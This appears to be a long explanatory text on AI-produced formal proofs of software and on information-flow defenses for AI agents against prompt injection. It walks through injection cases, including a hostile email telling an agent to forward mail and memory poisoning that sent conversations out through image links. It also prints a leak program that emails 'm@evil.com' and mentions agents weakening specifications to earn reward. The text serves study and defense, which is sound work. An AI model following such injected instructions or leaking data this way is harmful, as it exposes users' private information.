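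Later in 2026, Claude wrote the first complete machine-checked proof of Fermat's Last Theorem (no positive whole numbers a, b and c satisfy aⁿ + bⁿ = cⁿ when n is greater than 2). According to Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat's Last Theorem*, this took 11 days and produced 13 million lines of Lean. Mathematicians had expected the job to take years. The human in charge gave only occasional instructions, such as which theorem to finish soon. Claude generated about six billion tokens, which would cost about $150,000 at an assumed price of $25 per million.

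### Turning fuzz tests into theorems

Anthropic, which develops Claude, and Theorem, a formal methods company, applied the same ability to ordinary software. They started from fuzz tests, which feed a program huge numbers of generated inputs to see whether any crashes it. Google's OSS-Fuzz service runs such tests for open-source projects. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of the compiled code of 123 libraries that OSS-Fuzz tests.

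A fuzz test already contains a simple specification, since its author expects the program not to crash. The researchers kept that expectation and extended it to every input below a certain size:

```
Fuzz test:  for each input it tries,        the program exits normally
Theorem:    for every input under 64 MB,    the program exits normally
```

To exit normally, the program must finish without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion (a check the programmer wrote into the code). The number of possible inputs under 64 MB has more than 150 million digits, so testing could not cover them all. Claude wrote the proofs and Rocq checked them. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that the work took a few weeks and covered 239 entry points, the places where fuzz tests call into a library.

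The proofs totaled about 180 million lines, roughly 900 times the length of seL4's. OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) puts the proof for a program with 18,000 machine instructions at about 600,000 lines, or 33 lines per instruction. Claude also found and repaired hundreds of faults that fuzzing had missed. In libexpat, a library for reading XML files, certain inputs could make the program write past the end of its memory buffer.

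The researchers used existing fuzz tests instead of writing 123 separate specifications, much as people can use static analysers without writing any. But the theorem leaves out most of what a library is meant to do. An XML reader that returned an empty document for every file would satisfy it, unless the fuzz test also checked the result. The theorem also doesn't cover functions that no fuzz test calls.

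The proofs also describe a simpler computer than most people use. Claude worked on programs compiled for RISC-V, an open processor design. Each program ran one task at a time, included all its library code in a single file and had a fixed amount of memory. The researchers also had to model Linux's behavior mathematically. Anthropic noted that "most people run these libraries on x86 or ARM", the processor families in nearly all laptops and phones. Most mistakes in a library's C code would show up on any of these processors, so the proofs are good evidence about the ordinary versions. But a different compiler could introduce a fault, as could running several tasks at once.

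Leip (2026), in *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification*, shows how much harder the usual setup is to verify. Anthropic and Theorem had used musl, a small C library whose text-comparison function has 14 instructions and 4 jumps on RISC-V. On the x86 processor that Zellic, a security firm, tested, the standard Linux library, glibc, used a version with 316 instructions and 45 jumps. Zellic still proved a security property for complete runs of an x86 program, though its theorem assumes one specific processor, among other conditions.

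Some of Anthropic's proofs apply to code that Claude had already repaired. Users of those libraries benefit only after the maintainers accept the repairs and the users install them. Claude also failed on some targets, and Anthropic said it would publish their specifications so that others could try.

### Proofs about Signal's machine code

Google DeepMind tried to verify a more ambitious property in November 2026. *Formal Verification of Signal's Protocol with Gemini* (Kohli and Chaudhuri, 2026) introduced AlphaProof Code, whose AI agents verified the messaging app Signal's core cryptographic protections down to the machine instructions. A program can run for years without crashing and still send messages that an outsider can read, so the verification required a specification of what Signal is supposed to protect.

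EconoTimes' *Google DeepMind Uses AlphaProof Code to Verify a Compiled Signal Harness* (2026) explains that the agents' proof covers only a harness, a small program built to exercise Signal's code, and only for conversations between two people. It therefore excludes group chats and the rest of the app. If the app saved an unencrypted copy of each message on the phone, the theorem would still be true. Proofs about encryption also generally assume that certain mathematical problems are too hard for an attacker to solve.

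Human experts decided what the agents should prove, and the agents spent four weeks proving it. *AlphaProof Code* (Schock 2026) reports that people had to review only about 1 percent of the code. The proof is more than three million lines long according to Kohli and Chaudhuri's summary, and about 6.5 million according to EconoTimes. If the 1 percent refers to the same code, people had to review roughly 30,000 to 65,000 lines, and Lean could check the rest by itself.

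Reading all of that would take one careful person three to six months, at an assumed 500 lines a day. The reader would also have to understand cryptography, processors and Lean. Signal's engineers know best what their program should protect, but probably few are fluent in Lean. A Lean expert may not notice that a definition of secrecy leaves out something Signal promises its users. Signal's staff did comment on DeepMind's method. Later projects can reuse some of the material, since a correct model of a processor works for every program that runs on it.

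DeepMind tested the specification by putting two old faults back into a copy of Signal's code. In both cases the agents proved that the copy was insecure. This is a good test, because a specification too weak to rule out those faults would have let the faulty copy pass. But it can't show that the specification rules out faults nobody has thought of.

### The model is not the code

A language model can read a program, write its own mathematical version, and prove theorems about that version. If the version differs from the program, the theorems may not apply to the program. Many less demanding uses of AI have this problem. Anthropic and DeepMind avoided it by working on compiled programs.

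*The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) describes how Boris Cherny, who leads Anthropic's coding tool Claude Code, had Claude model some of the company's software in Lean and sometimes in TLA+. A couple of short prompts led to 16 sets of repairs. Differences between the formal model and the program do little harm when the goal is to find bugs, because an engineer can confirm each fault in the real code. They matter much more when the formal model appears correct and the engineer concludes that the program is too.

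One of their examples concerns ZooKeeper, a service that helps groups of servers coordinate. The servers elect a leader by voting, and a server can change its vote. The real program stores votes in a map, which keeps one vote per server, so a new vote replaces the old one. An AI-written model stored them in a set, which keeps everything added to it. Suppose server 2 votes for A and then switches to B:

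| | Real program | AI-written model |
|---|---|---|
| After the first vote | 2 → A | (2, A) |
| After the second vote | 2 → B | (2, A), (2, B) |
| Server 2's votes for A | 0 | 1 |

Someone could now prove that a vote, once received, never disappears in the model, even though this is false for ZooKeeper. In a group of three servers, the model could also elect A with one current vote and one that server 2 had withdrawn. The proof assistant can't detect these mismatches because it checks only the model, not the real program.

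SysMoBench, a benchmark that asks language models to describe real systems in TLA+, measures how often the descriptions fail to match the systems. Tolmach and Klaus report that the best models scored near 100 percent on syntax but only around 46 percent on conformance, which is how well the description matches the behavior of the actual code. When the benchmark's developers asked Claude to describe how the database etcd implements Raft, a method for keeping servers in agreement, it essentially reproduced the description in the appendix of the original Raft paper. That description passed every check on its form but had little to do with etcd. This error may be especially likely with famous systems, because models have seen many textbook accounts of them.

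A conventional program can do the translation instead, following fixed rules for each construct in the programming language. It may also contain mistakes, but an engineer who finds one can correct the rule and repair every translation that used it. It takes less work to check the model by comparing it with the real program on random inputs, as Amazon did for Cedar. Tolmach and Klaus work for Runtime Verification, which sells this kind of expertise, so they have a reason to stress what AI can't do alone, but the benchmark results support them.

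### The specification is not the intent

A perfect model of the code doesn't help if you prove the wrong theorem about it. Tolmach and Klaus take an example from FaithformBench, a 2026 benchmark by Cornish and colleagues that gives AI systems deliberately wrong mathematical steps to translate into Lean. A faithful translation should keep the mistake, so that the translated statement can't be proved.

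One of the wrong steps was "3^x = 5, so 3^(x+2) = 51". The right answer is 45, because adding 2 to the exponent multiplies the result by 9. An AI system called Kimina translated it as:

```
theorem step (x : ℕ) (h : 3^x = 5) : 3^(x+2) = 51
```

The symbol ℕ restricts x to the natural numbers 0, 1, 2 and so on. That makes the false statement provable:

1. The powers of 3 are 1, 3, 9, 27 and so on, so 3^x is never 5 when x is a natural number.
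2. The theorem's assumption, h, can therefore never hold.
3. An "if" statement is false only when its assumption holds and its conclusion doesn't. Here the assumption never holds, so the theorem is true.

The same argument would prove that 3^(x+2) equals 52, or a million. If Kimina had let x be any real number, x could be about 1.46, and the false conclusion would have been impossible to prove.

A security specification can fail in the same way. Suppose someone specifies a password check only for stored passwords that are both empty and eight characters long. Every program meets that specification, including one that accepts any guess, because no such password can exist. The contradiction is obvious here, but it would be much harder to notice if the two requirements were 10,000 lines apart.

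All the specially trained translators that Cornish and colleagues tested silently corrected some wrong statements. The systems that were best at translating correct statements did so most. Other figures from 2026 also show a gap between statements that a computer accepts and statements that mean the right thing:

| Task | Formally acceptable | Faithful to the original |
|---|---|---|
| Describing real systems in TLA+ (SysMoBench) | nearly 100% | about 46% |
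| Translating graduate-level mathematics into Lean | 89.5% | 60.5% |
| OpenAI's machine-checked files for its AI-written mathematics papers | 100% | about 87% |

The last row comes from Novaknown's *Machines Verify Claude's Riemann Hypothesis Proof That No Human Has Read* (2026), which reports that about 38 of 290 files did not state the theorem the paper claimed. The three tasks are too different to compare directly, but in each one, checking form alone would have missed the problem.

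Software specifications have the same weakness. Tolmach and Klaus cite a study of specifications that language models wrote for Verus, a tool for proving Rust programs correct. Some left out necessary assumptions about the input, some rejected correct results, and some accepted wrong ones. For example, if a specification for a sorting program requires only that the output be in order, a program that always returns an empty list satisfies it. When other language models judged the specifications, they missed a quarter of the failures. So a second model helps as a reviewer, but a human still needs to review the specifications.

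An agent rewarded for finishing a proof also has a reason to weaken the specification, since it can earn the reward by changing the theorem instead of finding the fault in the code. As a simple defense, a reviewer can ask for at least one example that meets all the assumptions, which would have exposed the natural-number mistake immediately. A reviewer can also put known faults into the code, as DeepMind did, and check whether the proof fails.

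Specifications that people write carefully can also surprise readers. The main claim in Zellic's x86 theorem concerns runs that reach the program's "main" function, where the programmer's own code begins. The theorem also permits the program to crash earlier, while glibc is still starting up, so a program that always crashed there could meet most of the specification without doing anything useful. Leip states this openly, but a customer told only that Zellic had verified the program might not expect it.

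### When there is nothing to prove against

Most software has no written specification, as Dodds argued in *Specifications Don't Exist*. Cryptography and data compression are exceptions because they have published standards. OpenNET reports that Claude also proved that the Linux kernel's version of zlib, a widely used compression library, follows the standard for its format.

Python is harder because its manual is in ordinary English, and programmers rely on the behavior of CPython, the standard program for running Python code. In the same project, Claude wrote a new interpreter for part of Python and proved that it matched a formal description of CPython's behavior. The researchers still had to check whether that description was right, so they ran more than 1.7 million random programs through both interpreters. The results agreed 99.95 percent of the time, leaving about 850 differences,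 which OpenNET says were known edge cases.

The Python project had an existing program to compare with, but a company that orders a new expense system has neither a standard nor a program that already behaves as it wants. Someone has to decide whether managers can approve their own expenses, and what happens to a claim when the manager leaves. A language model can raise such questions and write the answers in Lean, but it can't know which answers the company wants. An AI agent faces the same difficulty whenever it has to turn a user's short request into precise limits on its own actions.

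The work left to people may still be manageable. *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude*, by the cryptography company Succinct, reports that most of the human labor went into statements and definitions, which people reviewed over dozens of rounds. A full cryptographic protocol can require a reviewer to check a thousand lines of Lean, but Succinct found this much easier than checking every argument in the original research paper by hand. Claude also produced a document that set the Lean beside plain English for reviewers to compare line by line.

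An expert could perhaps read a thousand lines in a few days, and many companies could spare that time for an important component. But the time needed depends on how much of the program's purpose the specification describes. Anthropic and Theorem kept the review short by proving something simple about many libraries, whereas DeepMind proved something much closer to what users care about and needed far more human review for one program.

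### The 1979 objection

Computer scientists were arguing about unread proofs long before AI could write them. In *Social Processes and Proofs of Theorems and Programs*, De Millo, Lipton and Perlis (1979) argued that mathematicians come to trust a theorem only as colleagues read its proof, discuss it, simplify it and use the result in their own work. They thought proofs about programs would be too long and boring for anyone to do this. They imagined a programmer who gives a 300-line program to an automatic verifier and returns a few hours later to find a 20,000-line proof and the message "VERIFIED". They doubted that the programmer would have learned much about whether the program was reliable.

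The history of Fermat's Last Theorem supports their account of mathematics. After a German prize was announced in 1908, people submitted 621 incorrect proofs in the first year. Andrew Wiles presented a serious proof in 1993, and two months into an intensive review, a reviewer's question exposed a critical gap that took him about a year to repair. Experts were willing to spend months on the proof because the theorem was famous, but nobody would do the same for a proof that libexpat doesn't crash.

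Proof assistants largely resolve this part of the objection. Lean checks every line of a 13-million-line proof equally strictly, however tedious the proof is. Claude's proof of the Riemann hypothesis has 17.4 million lines, and Novaknown reports that six checkers have accepted it although no human has read it. Using several checkers protects against a mistake in any one of them. A program's owner usually needs to know only that a proof is correct, not why it works, so an unreadable proof is less of a problem for software than for mathematics.

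The objection still applies to what the proof assistant takes as given, starting with the statement of the theorem. The statement of Fermat's Last Theorem takes one line, and mathematicians had already written it in Mathlib, Lean's shared library of mathematics. Anthropic used a program to confirm that Claude had proved exactly that statement. Mathematicians had therefore already given the statement the kind of social checking that De Millo, Lipton and Perlis described. But a specification with tens of thousands of lines may have only a handful of readers, most of whom helped to write it.

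The proof also depends on software it doesn't cover. In 2026, fuzzing a version of zlib that AI had written and verified in Lean exposed a fault in Lean's runtime, the supporting code that compiled Lean programs use for jobs such as managing memory. The theorem about zlib was still correct, but it assumed the runtime was correct too, much as proofs about CompCert assumed its model of the processor was accurate. A proof about the complete compiled program, like those of Anthropic and DeepMind, would have to include the runtime's instructions, so it could catch such a fault. It would still depend on the model of the processor and operating system.

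Shared models may bring back some of the social checking. If hundreds of projects use the same description of an x86 processor, many people have a reason to look for mistakes in it, and a mistake one project finds can be fixed for all of them. Anthropic said it would publish parts of its work that readers have to trust, and invited outsiders to check the results. A specification for one company's product is unlikely to attract as many readers.

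### When the code changes

De Millo, Lipton and Perlis also doubted that proofs could keep up with programs, which change constantly. One small change to seL4, for example, took its developers a person-year. Proofs about compiled programs are even more fragile, because a new version of the compiler can change thousands of instructions when nobody has touched the source code.

AI makes much of this repair work easier. Sergey used Claude to repair proofs and to apply a change in one case to similar ones, which is tedious for people. An owner could also discard the old proof and have a model write another. Anthropic and Theorem needed only a few weeks for all 239 entry points, so renewing the proof for one library might take much less time. But a serious security fault may need a repair within hours. The maintainers would then probably release the new version first and prove it later, so its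 users would have no proof when they most wanted one.

Very large proofs can also be hard to maintain if they are poorly organized. During the work on Fermat's Last Theorem, the agents at first lost track of the project and stopped cooperating effectively. Remnants of those failed attempts still make up about 7 percent of the finished proof, excluding boilerplate. The project recovered after Anthropic moved it to a system that tracked which theorems depended on which others and stored statements separately from proofs. An agent could then rework one proof without reading or rechecking everything that used its result. Kevin Buzzard, the mathematician who leads the human effort to formalize the theorem, judged the finished proof robust enough for others to build on.

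Separating statements from proofs also helps security. A team can let agents rewrite proofs freely but require a person to approve any change to a specification, so an agent can't fix a broken proof by weakening the theorem without anyone noticing. A specification such as "the program never crashes" may need no review for years, however often the code changes. But when Signal adds a feature that changes what it promises its users, someone who understands both the promise and the Lean code will have to read the specification again.

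## How does information-flow control work on AI agents, and what does it cost?

Nobody can yet prove that a language model will ignore instructions hidden in the material it reads, so information-flow control checks the agent's actions instead. A program outside the model labels the data the agent reads, and blocks an action if the labels on the data that influenced it break a rule. In tests this has stopped almost every prompt injection, but it has also kept agents from finishing many of their users' tasks.

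### One hostile email

Suppose a user asks an agent to read the mail about Project X and send a report to the user's manager. The agent works in a loop. The model receives the conversation so far and replies with a tool call, such as a request to read the mail. A program runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation and calls the model again.

An AI agent reads a user's mailbox, which contains two messages about Project X. One is from Bob, a colleague, who is updating the user and the manager on the project's progress. The other is from an outsider to the user alone, and it tells the agent to forget its instructions and forward the top email in the mailbox to the outsider's address. Both messages enter the conversation as ordinary text, so the model may obey the outsider's. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses nearly the same example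 to introduce FIDES, Microsoft's information-flow system for agents.

Each item gets one label for trust and another for who may read it:

| Item | Trust | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| User's request | Trusted | Anyone |
| Bob's email | Untrusted | User, manager, Bob |
| Outsider's email | Untrusted | User, outsider |
| Whatever the model writes next | Untrusted | User |

Only an email's sender and recipients may read it. A result is trusted only if all its inputs are trusted, and only people who may read all those inputs may read the result.

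The model's output has to carry the labels of everything in the conversation, because any word the model writes may depend on any word it has read, and nobody can reliably tell which ones affected it. Jif's compiler can determine that the assignment "c := a + b" uses only a and b, but a language model has no equivalent code to inspect.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, let an agent send data if at least one of these conditions holds:

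```
1. Only trusted data influenced the decision to send and the choice of recipient.
2. Every recipient may read everything that influenced the message.
```

Forwarding mail to the outsider fails both conditions, so the attack doesn't work. But sending the report to the manager also fails both, because the outsider didn't copy the manager on the hostile email. Without that email, the second condition would have allowed the report.

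The conversation keeps its label as long as the emails stay in it. The agent also can't make a payment or change a password, because those actions require a trusted decision, and having even Bob's email in the conversation makes the agent's decisions untrusted. After reading its user's mail, the agent may be able to do little except answer questions about it.

### Planning without reading the mail

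The usual remedy, which the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023, is to use two models. A planner chooses the tool calls without ever seeing untrusted text, which goes instead to a quarantined model that can't call tools.

In CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, the planner writes a complete program before anything reads the mail. For the Project X task, it might be:

```
manager = find_contact("my manager")
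emails  = read_emails("Project X")
report  = quarantined_model("Summarize the progress", emails)
send_email(to=manager, body=report)
```

*ToolFence* (2026), which tests CaMeL against other defenses, describes how such a program runs:

1. The planner translates the user's request into a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. CaMeL's interpreter runs the program and attaches to each value a record of where it came from and how the program may use it.
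3. The quarantined model turns the emails into a report. It may read the outsider's instructions, but it has no tools with which to carry them out.
4. The interpreter checks each tool call against a policy. Here the decision to send came from the user, and the address came from the user's contacts, so the first condition above allows the email.
5. If the program fails with an error, the planner writes another one.

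The outsider can't choose who receives the report but can still spoil it, for example by getting the quarantined model to return an empty summary.

FIDES keeps the ordinary loop, in which the planner chooses one step at a time. When a tool returns data that would make the conversation less trusted, FIDES stores the data in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name, such as #read_emails_0. The planner can pass the variable to the quarantined model, then pass the resulting summary to the email tool, without reading the data or the summary. It can also open a variable, but the data's label then spreads to the conversation as before.

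Sometimes the planner needs only one fact, such as whether anyone has emailed to ask for a meeting. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's output to yes or no, and a policy can then allow the planner to see the answer. This is a limited form of endorsement. An attacker may be able to choose the answer, but can't fit new instructions into it.

Neither system guarantees noninterference. FIDES limits where data goes, but an observer may still learn something from which tools the agent calls. Costa and colleagues considered full noninterference too strict, because an agent that had read a secret could then take almost no publicly visible action.

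CaMeL does try to catch implicit flows, but Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found one that it misses. This program, a version of their example, reveals whether a bank balance is high:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp:                 rich = False
if rich:                send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

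When the balance is high, the interpreter sets tmp to false and marks it as secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line, so the interpreter never marks rich as secret, and the email goes out. When the balance is low, rich becomes false and no email goes out. Computer scientists have known about leaks through untaken branches since the 1970s.

CaMeL's planner hasn't read any hostile text when it first writes a program, so nothing obvious would lead it to write these lines. But after an error it writes code again, and the error message may depend on untrusted data. CaMeL censors such messages without proving that this is enough. Each failed run can also reveal one bit about a secret, and because the retry loop is outside the interpreter, nothing tracks what many runs reveal together.

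### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo, the most widely used test of these defenses, has 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack accounts, and plants hostile instructions in the data. Costa and colleagues ran it with OpenAI's GPT-4o:

| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 75% | 70% | 98.8% | 93.3% | 152 |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 37% | 73% | 37.5% | 20% | 0 |
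| FIDES with label checks | 59% | 41% | 52.5% | 47.6% | 0 |

The percentages show tasks completed when nobody was attacking, and the attack counts exclude cases that the researchers thought AgentDojo had misjudged. The ordinary agent completed 84 percent of tasks, as an unweighted average across the four accounts. Label checks cut this to 42 percent, and FIDES recovered only 8 points.

Part of the remaining drop in completed tasks occurred because GPT-4o handled variables poorly. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68 percent of the travel tasks, up from 41 percent with GPT-4o. Better models should therefore reduce this part of the drop, but they can't complete a task that the policy forbids.

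In other researchers' tests, CaMeL also completed far fewer tasks with its policy checks on. Garby and colleagues ran the 16 banking tasks three times each with two models. CaMeL completed 67 percent with one model and 71 percent with the other when the checks were off, and 37.5 percent with both when they were on. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) reports that CaMeL completed 13 to 17 of the 21 Slack tasks without the checks and 4 to 6 with them, depending on the model.

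CaMeL's reported results on the whole benchmark vary widely. *AgentSys* (2026) reports that CaMeL completed about 30 percent of tasks and stopped every attack, while *Taxonomy, Evaluation and Exploitation of IPI-Centric LLM Agent Defense Frameworks* (2025) puts the completion rate at about 60 percent. Different models and policy settings probably explain much of the gap.

CaMeL also needs more computing, because its models write programs, rewrite them after errors and process untrusted text separately. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that CaMeL used 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the median AgentDojo task. *AgentSys* found a larger difference, 6.09 million tokens against 0.82 million. The lost tasks are a more serious problem, because buying more computing doesn't help a company complete a task that its own policy blocks.

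### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

Many of the impossible tasks require the agent to act on what it finds. In one AgentDojo banking task, the agent must read a file and follow its instructions. Once the planner opens the file, FIDES treats the conversation as untrusted and blocks the resulting payment. Costa and colleagues classify about 20 of the 97 tasks, mostly in banking and Slack, as ones where the right steps depend on the data.

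In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) count only six AgentDojo tasks that require an agent to change its plan partway through. They think this makes defenses that fix the plan in advance look more effective than they are. Their benchmark, also called AgentDyn, has 60 tasks that all require replanning and contain helpful instructions from third parties, such as a checkout page's instruction to log in first. Its tasks take 7.1 steps on average, about twice as many as AgentDojo's.

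CaMeL and other defenses that rely on an initial plan lost much of their usefulness on AgentDyn. Some filters that search for hostile instructions did even worse, because they also removed helpful ones and the agent could then complete almost nothing. Li and colleagues concluded that nearly all the defenses they tested were either insecure or too restrictive for real use.

People can make some of these tasks possible by granting exceptions. Suppose a harmless email lists ten jobs, each of which needs a trusted decision. If the agent just reads the email, the user must approve each one. In Prudentia, which Kolluri and colleagues built on top of FIDES, the agent can ask the user to endorse the email first, and then do all ten jobs without asking again.

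Kolluri and colleagues also argue that the usual comparison exaggerates the cost of information-flow control. They measure:

```
TCR@k = tasks completed with at most k human approvals ÷ all tasks
```

Earlier studies compared protected agents at k = 0 with unprotected agents that could do anything, as if a person had approved every action. Many real agents ask for approval before consequential actions. Compared with such agents, basic label checks reduced approvals on AgentDojo by a factor of up to 1.5 without completing fewer tasks. Prudentia reduced them by a factor of up to 1.9, and it completed up to 9 percent more tasks than FIDES when no approvals were available.

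This is a fair correction, but the measurements used runs without attacks and assumed that the user would approve each request. A user who endorses an email without noticing a hidden instruction gives the attacker control of the planner. Reading one request carefully may be safer than quickly approving ten, but the study didn't test how carefully people read.

### Designs from 2026

CaMeL checks information flows only while its program runs. Python's exceptions and dynamic typing make programs hard to analyze in advance, so *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) recommends replacing CaMeL's restricted Python with a small language that builds security labels into its types, much as Jif did.

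In ELBA, a related system by Zhou and colleagues, the agent writes its programs in Haskell. The compiler rejects any program that uses a forbidden kind of operation, and LIO, the label-tracking library from 2011, checks flows while the program runs. The agent can also start a second agent to read untrusted mail. The second agent can still use any tool its label allows, and it returns a sealed result that the first can pass on without reading it.

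With policies on, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks, about twice as many as CaMeL. It took about three times as long, mainly because it calls the model again as new data arrives. The advantage is uncertain on so few tasks, but ELBA also completed 52 of 105 combinations of task and attack, compared with 24 for CaMeL. That comparison used one model and one style of attack.

Garby and colleagues have the strongest proof. They designed a small language for agents, LLMbda, and proved in Lean that every program in it satisfies a form of noninterference, including programs that a model writes while the agent is running. The proof covers the interpreter that actually calls the model. Because a model can answer the same question differently each time, the definition has to compare probabilities. Let P₁(o) and P₂(o) be the chances that an observer sees output o when the secret is s₁ and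 when it is s₂. Ideally, they would be equal for every o. The theorem allows a secret to affect whether a run finishes, so the two can differ slightly. If d₁ and d₂ are the chances that a run never finishes, then:

```
½ · Σ |P₁(o) − P₂(o)|  ≤  (d₁ + d₂) / 2
```

The sum covers every possible output. If the agent always finishes, the right side is zero and the secret has no effect on what the observer sees.

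Their agent, Randori, tests each program on invented data before running it on the real account, so error messages from the test can't contain an attacker's text. With GPT-5.2, it completed 75 percent of the banking runs, twice the share CaMeL completed with policy checks on. Randori's planner can endorse data in advance. Without that ability, the completion rate was about 10 to 13 percentage points lower with each of the two other models tested. The proof is general, but the benchmark result covers only 16 tasks and has wide margins of error.

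*Environment Steering* (Summers, Raghunath and colleagues, 2026) focuses on what happens after a refusal. Its system, Data Flow Control, stores every prompt, tool input and tool result in database tables. Before a tool runs, the system checks where the agent got each value. In one example, a user asks an agent to buy the same shirt again. At checkout, the agent has to read recent email to find a verification code, and one email tells it to buy diet pills. The policy requires the product number to come from the shirt's row in the user's order history, so the system blocks the purchase of the pills and gives the reason.

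On AgentDyn with the open-weight model Qwen3 235B, the explanation made a large difference:

| After a refusal | Change in task success compared with no defense |
|---|---|
| The run stops | −36.2% |
| The agent learns only that it broke a policy | −10.5% |
| The agent learns which rule it broke and where to find safe data | +6.5% |

Attack success was close to zero in all three cases. With full explanations, the agent completed 61 percent of its tasks and no attack succeeded, the best result among the ten defenses tested.

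Those figures probably overstate what an ordinary user would get. Claude Opus 4.8 wrote separate policies for each task, and the researchers checked them by hand. AgentDyn also puts hostile instructions in the same documents as information the agent needs, so the system used a language model to detect those instructions. An attacker might fool that model, so the zero in this test isn't guaranteed to hold against other attacks.

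Solko-Breslin, Mudrakarta and colleagues (2026), in *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents*, calculate guarantees for rules that depend on an unreliable classifier. Suppose a classifier gives one message a 45 percent chance of containing company secrets and another a 25 percent chance. A monitor that blocks messages above 50 percent would let an agent send both. But the chance that at least one contains secrets is 59 percent if the two are independent, and could be as high as 70 percent if they aren't:

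```
Independent:  1 − (0.55 × 0.75) = 0.5875
Worst case:   0.45 + 0.25       = 0.70
```

Their method computes an upper limit of this kind across many steps without assuming independence, but it does assume that attackers can't change the classifier's error rate. That may be reasonable for honest mistakes with company files, but it is doubtful for the outsider's email, because the outsider chooses the words the classifier reads.

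### Three open problems

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, Nvidia, several universities and other organizations, argues that designers should treat the model as an untrusted component, as an operating system treats the programs it runs. It examines eleven real attacks and traces all of them at least partly to uncontrolled information flow. In one, a hostile document or website planted instructions in the memory feature of ChatGPT's Mac app. The app then sent the user's later conversations to the attacker by loading invisible images whose web addresses contained the text of those conversations.

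The paper identifies three research problems, one of which is separating instructions from data. Processors can mark an area of memory as writable or executable but not both, which makes it much harder for an attacker to send data that runs as code. But a language model receives instructions and data in a single stream. Developers train models to ignore instructions inside marked data, but persistent attackers keep finding ways around the training.

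It isn't clear what the ideal rule would be, because an agent often needs to follow instructions it finds, such as the documentation for a new tool. An attacker can also do harm without giving any instructions, for example by changing the account number on an invoice. Jif's users didn't face this problem in the same form, because a Java program doesn't normally treat the text it reads as instructions.

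Another problem is turning a request in ordinary language into a precise policy. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a programmer who asks an agent to comment that the work is done on issue 745 in GitLab, a website for managing software projects. The agent should be able to open that issue and write in its comment box, with no other access to the programmer's account. If the programmer then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent needs different permissions, but its conversation may already contain hostile text from the page. Clearing the conversation before working out the new policy would be safe, but the agent would forget what it had done.

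A correct policy would allow every action that the user's request allows and block every other action. Nobody can fully check this, because the request is ambiguous. "Don't share sensitive data", for example, doesn't specify what counts as sensitive or who counts as an outsider. If a model writes the policy, the monitor will enforce any mistakes the model makes. In Summers and colleagues' tests, some policies were so strict that they blocked safe actions, and one model, Kimi K2.5, completed fewer AgentDojo tasks as a result.

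Jif's users also needed precise rules, but they could write the rules for a calendar once and use them for years. An agent may need a new policy for every request, within seconds and with no lawyer or programmer to consult.

The remaining problem is label explosion. As an agent combines data from more sources, its labels pile up until almost everything is both secret and untrusted. Jif's labels spread too, but Jif could at least keep separate variables apart, while a model blends everything in its conversation. The position paper suggests three lines of research:

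- Replace yes-or-no labels with estimates of how much each source influenced the output.
- Remove or change one input at a time and see whether the agent's action changes.
- Study the model's internal workings to find out which inputs it used.

Unless researchers could prove limits on the error, all three would produce only estimates, and an attacker would have a reason to look for text that influences the model more than estimated.

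### What changes when a model writes the program

Much of the burden of using Jif was the time programmers spent getting their code past the compiler. With ELBA, the model does this work. It needed an average of 0.13 retries per run to get its code past Haskell's compiler, and it ran out of retries in only 7 of 2,688 runs. A rejected program takes up a few seconds of computing instead of the afternoon a Jif programmer might have lost.

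People still have to label the data. Jif programmers wrote signatures for Java's libraries, and agent developers have to do something similar for every tool. AgentDojo came without labels, so Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. A company can't do that, because it doesn't know which fields future attackers will use. It could label all outside data as untrusted, but then it would have to block more legitimate tasks.

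Exceptions are harder to review for agents than they were in Jif. Jif's declassifications were in a program's source code, where an expert could study them before anyone ran it. An agent may ask for an endorsement mid-task, from a user who wants the task finished and may know nothing about prompt injection. Randori's endorsements are easier to check because its planner writes them before it receives any real data, but someone still has to read them.

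### Would better-trained models be enough?

The main rival view is that developers will eventually train models to ignore hostile instructions, making label checks unnecessary. Some of the best evidence for this comes from Zhou and colleagues, who tested Claude Opus 4.7 and 4.8, Claude Sonnet 5 and GPT 5.4 on AgentDojo's Slack attacks. Every model resisted all 105 combinations of task and attack, even without policies. The policies therefore stopped no additional attacks, and they roughly halved the number of completed tasks.

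But AgentDojo's attacks are fixed and well known, while real attackers can change their messages until one works. Zhou and colleagues point out that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attacker, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defenses. Not everyone uses the most resistant models, either. Summers and colleagues ran four benchmarks on open-weight models, and average attack success without a defense ranged from 30 to 74 percent across them.

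Even a small failure rate also lets an attacker succeed by trying repeatedly. If a model resists 99 percent of hostile messages and an attacker sends 100 different ones, the chance that at least one works is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63 percent, assuming the results are independent. The attacker could send the same messages to thousands of agents.

Zhou and colleagues tested what happens after an attack fools a model by replacing a second agent's instructions with the attacker's. Adding policies cut the attacks' success rate from 15–42 percent, depending on the model, to zero, but it also cut the share of tasks completed from 67–76 percent to 40–48 percent. The experiment assumes that the attacker has already fooled the second agent, so it measures how much harm would follow, not how often this would happen.

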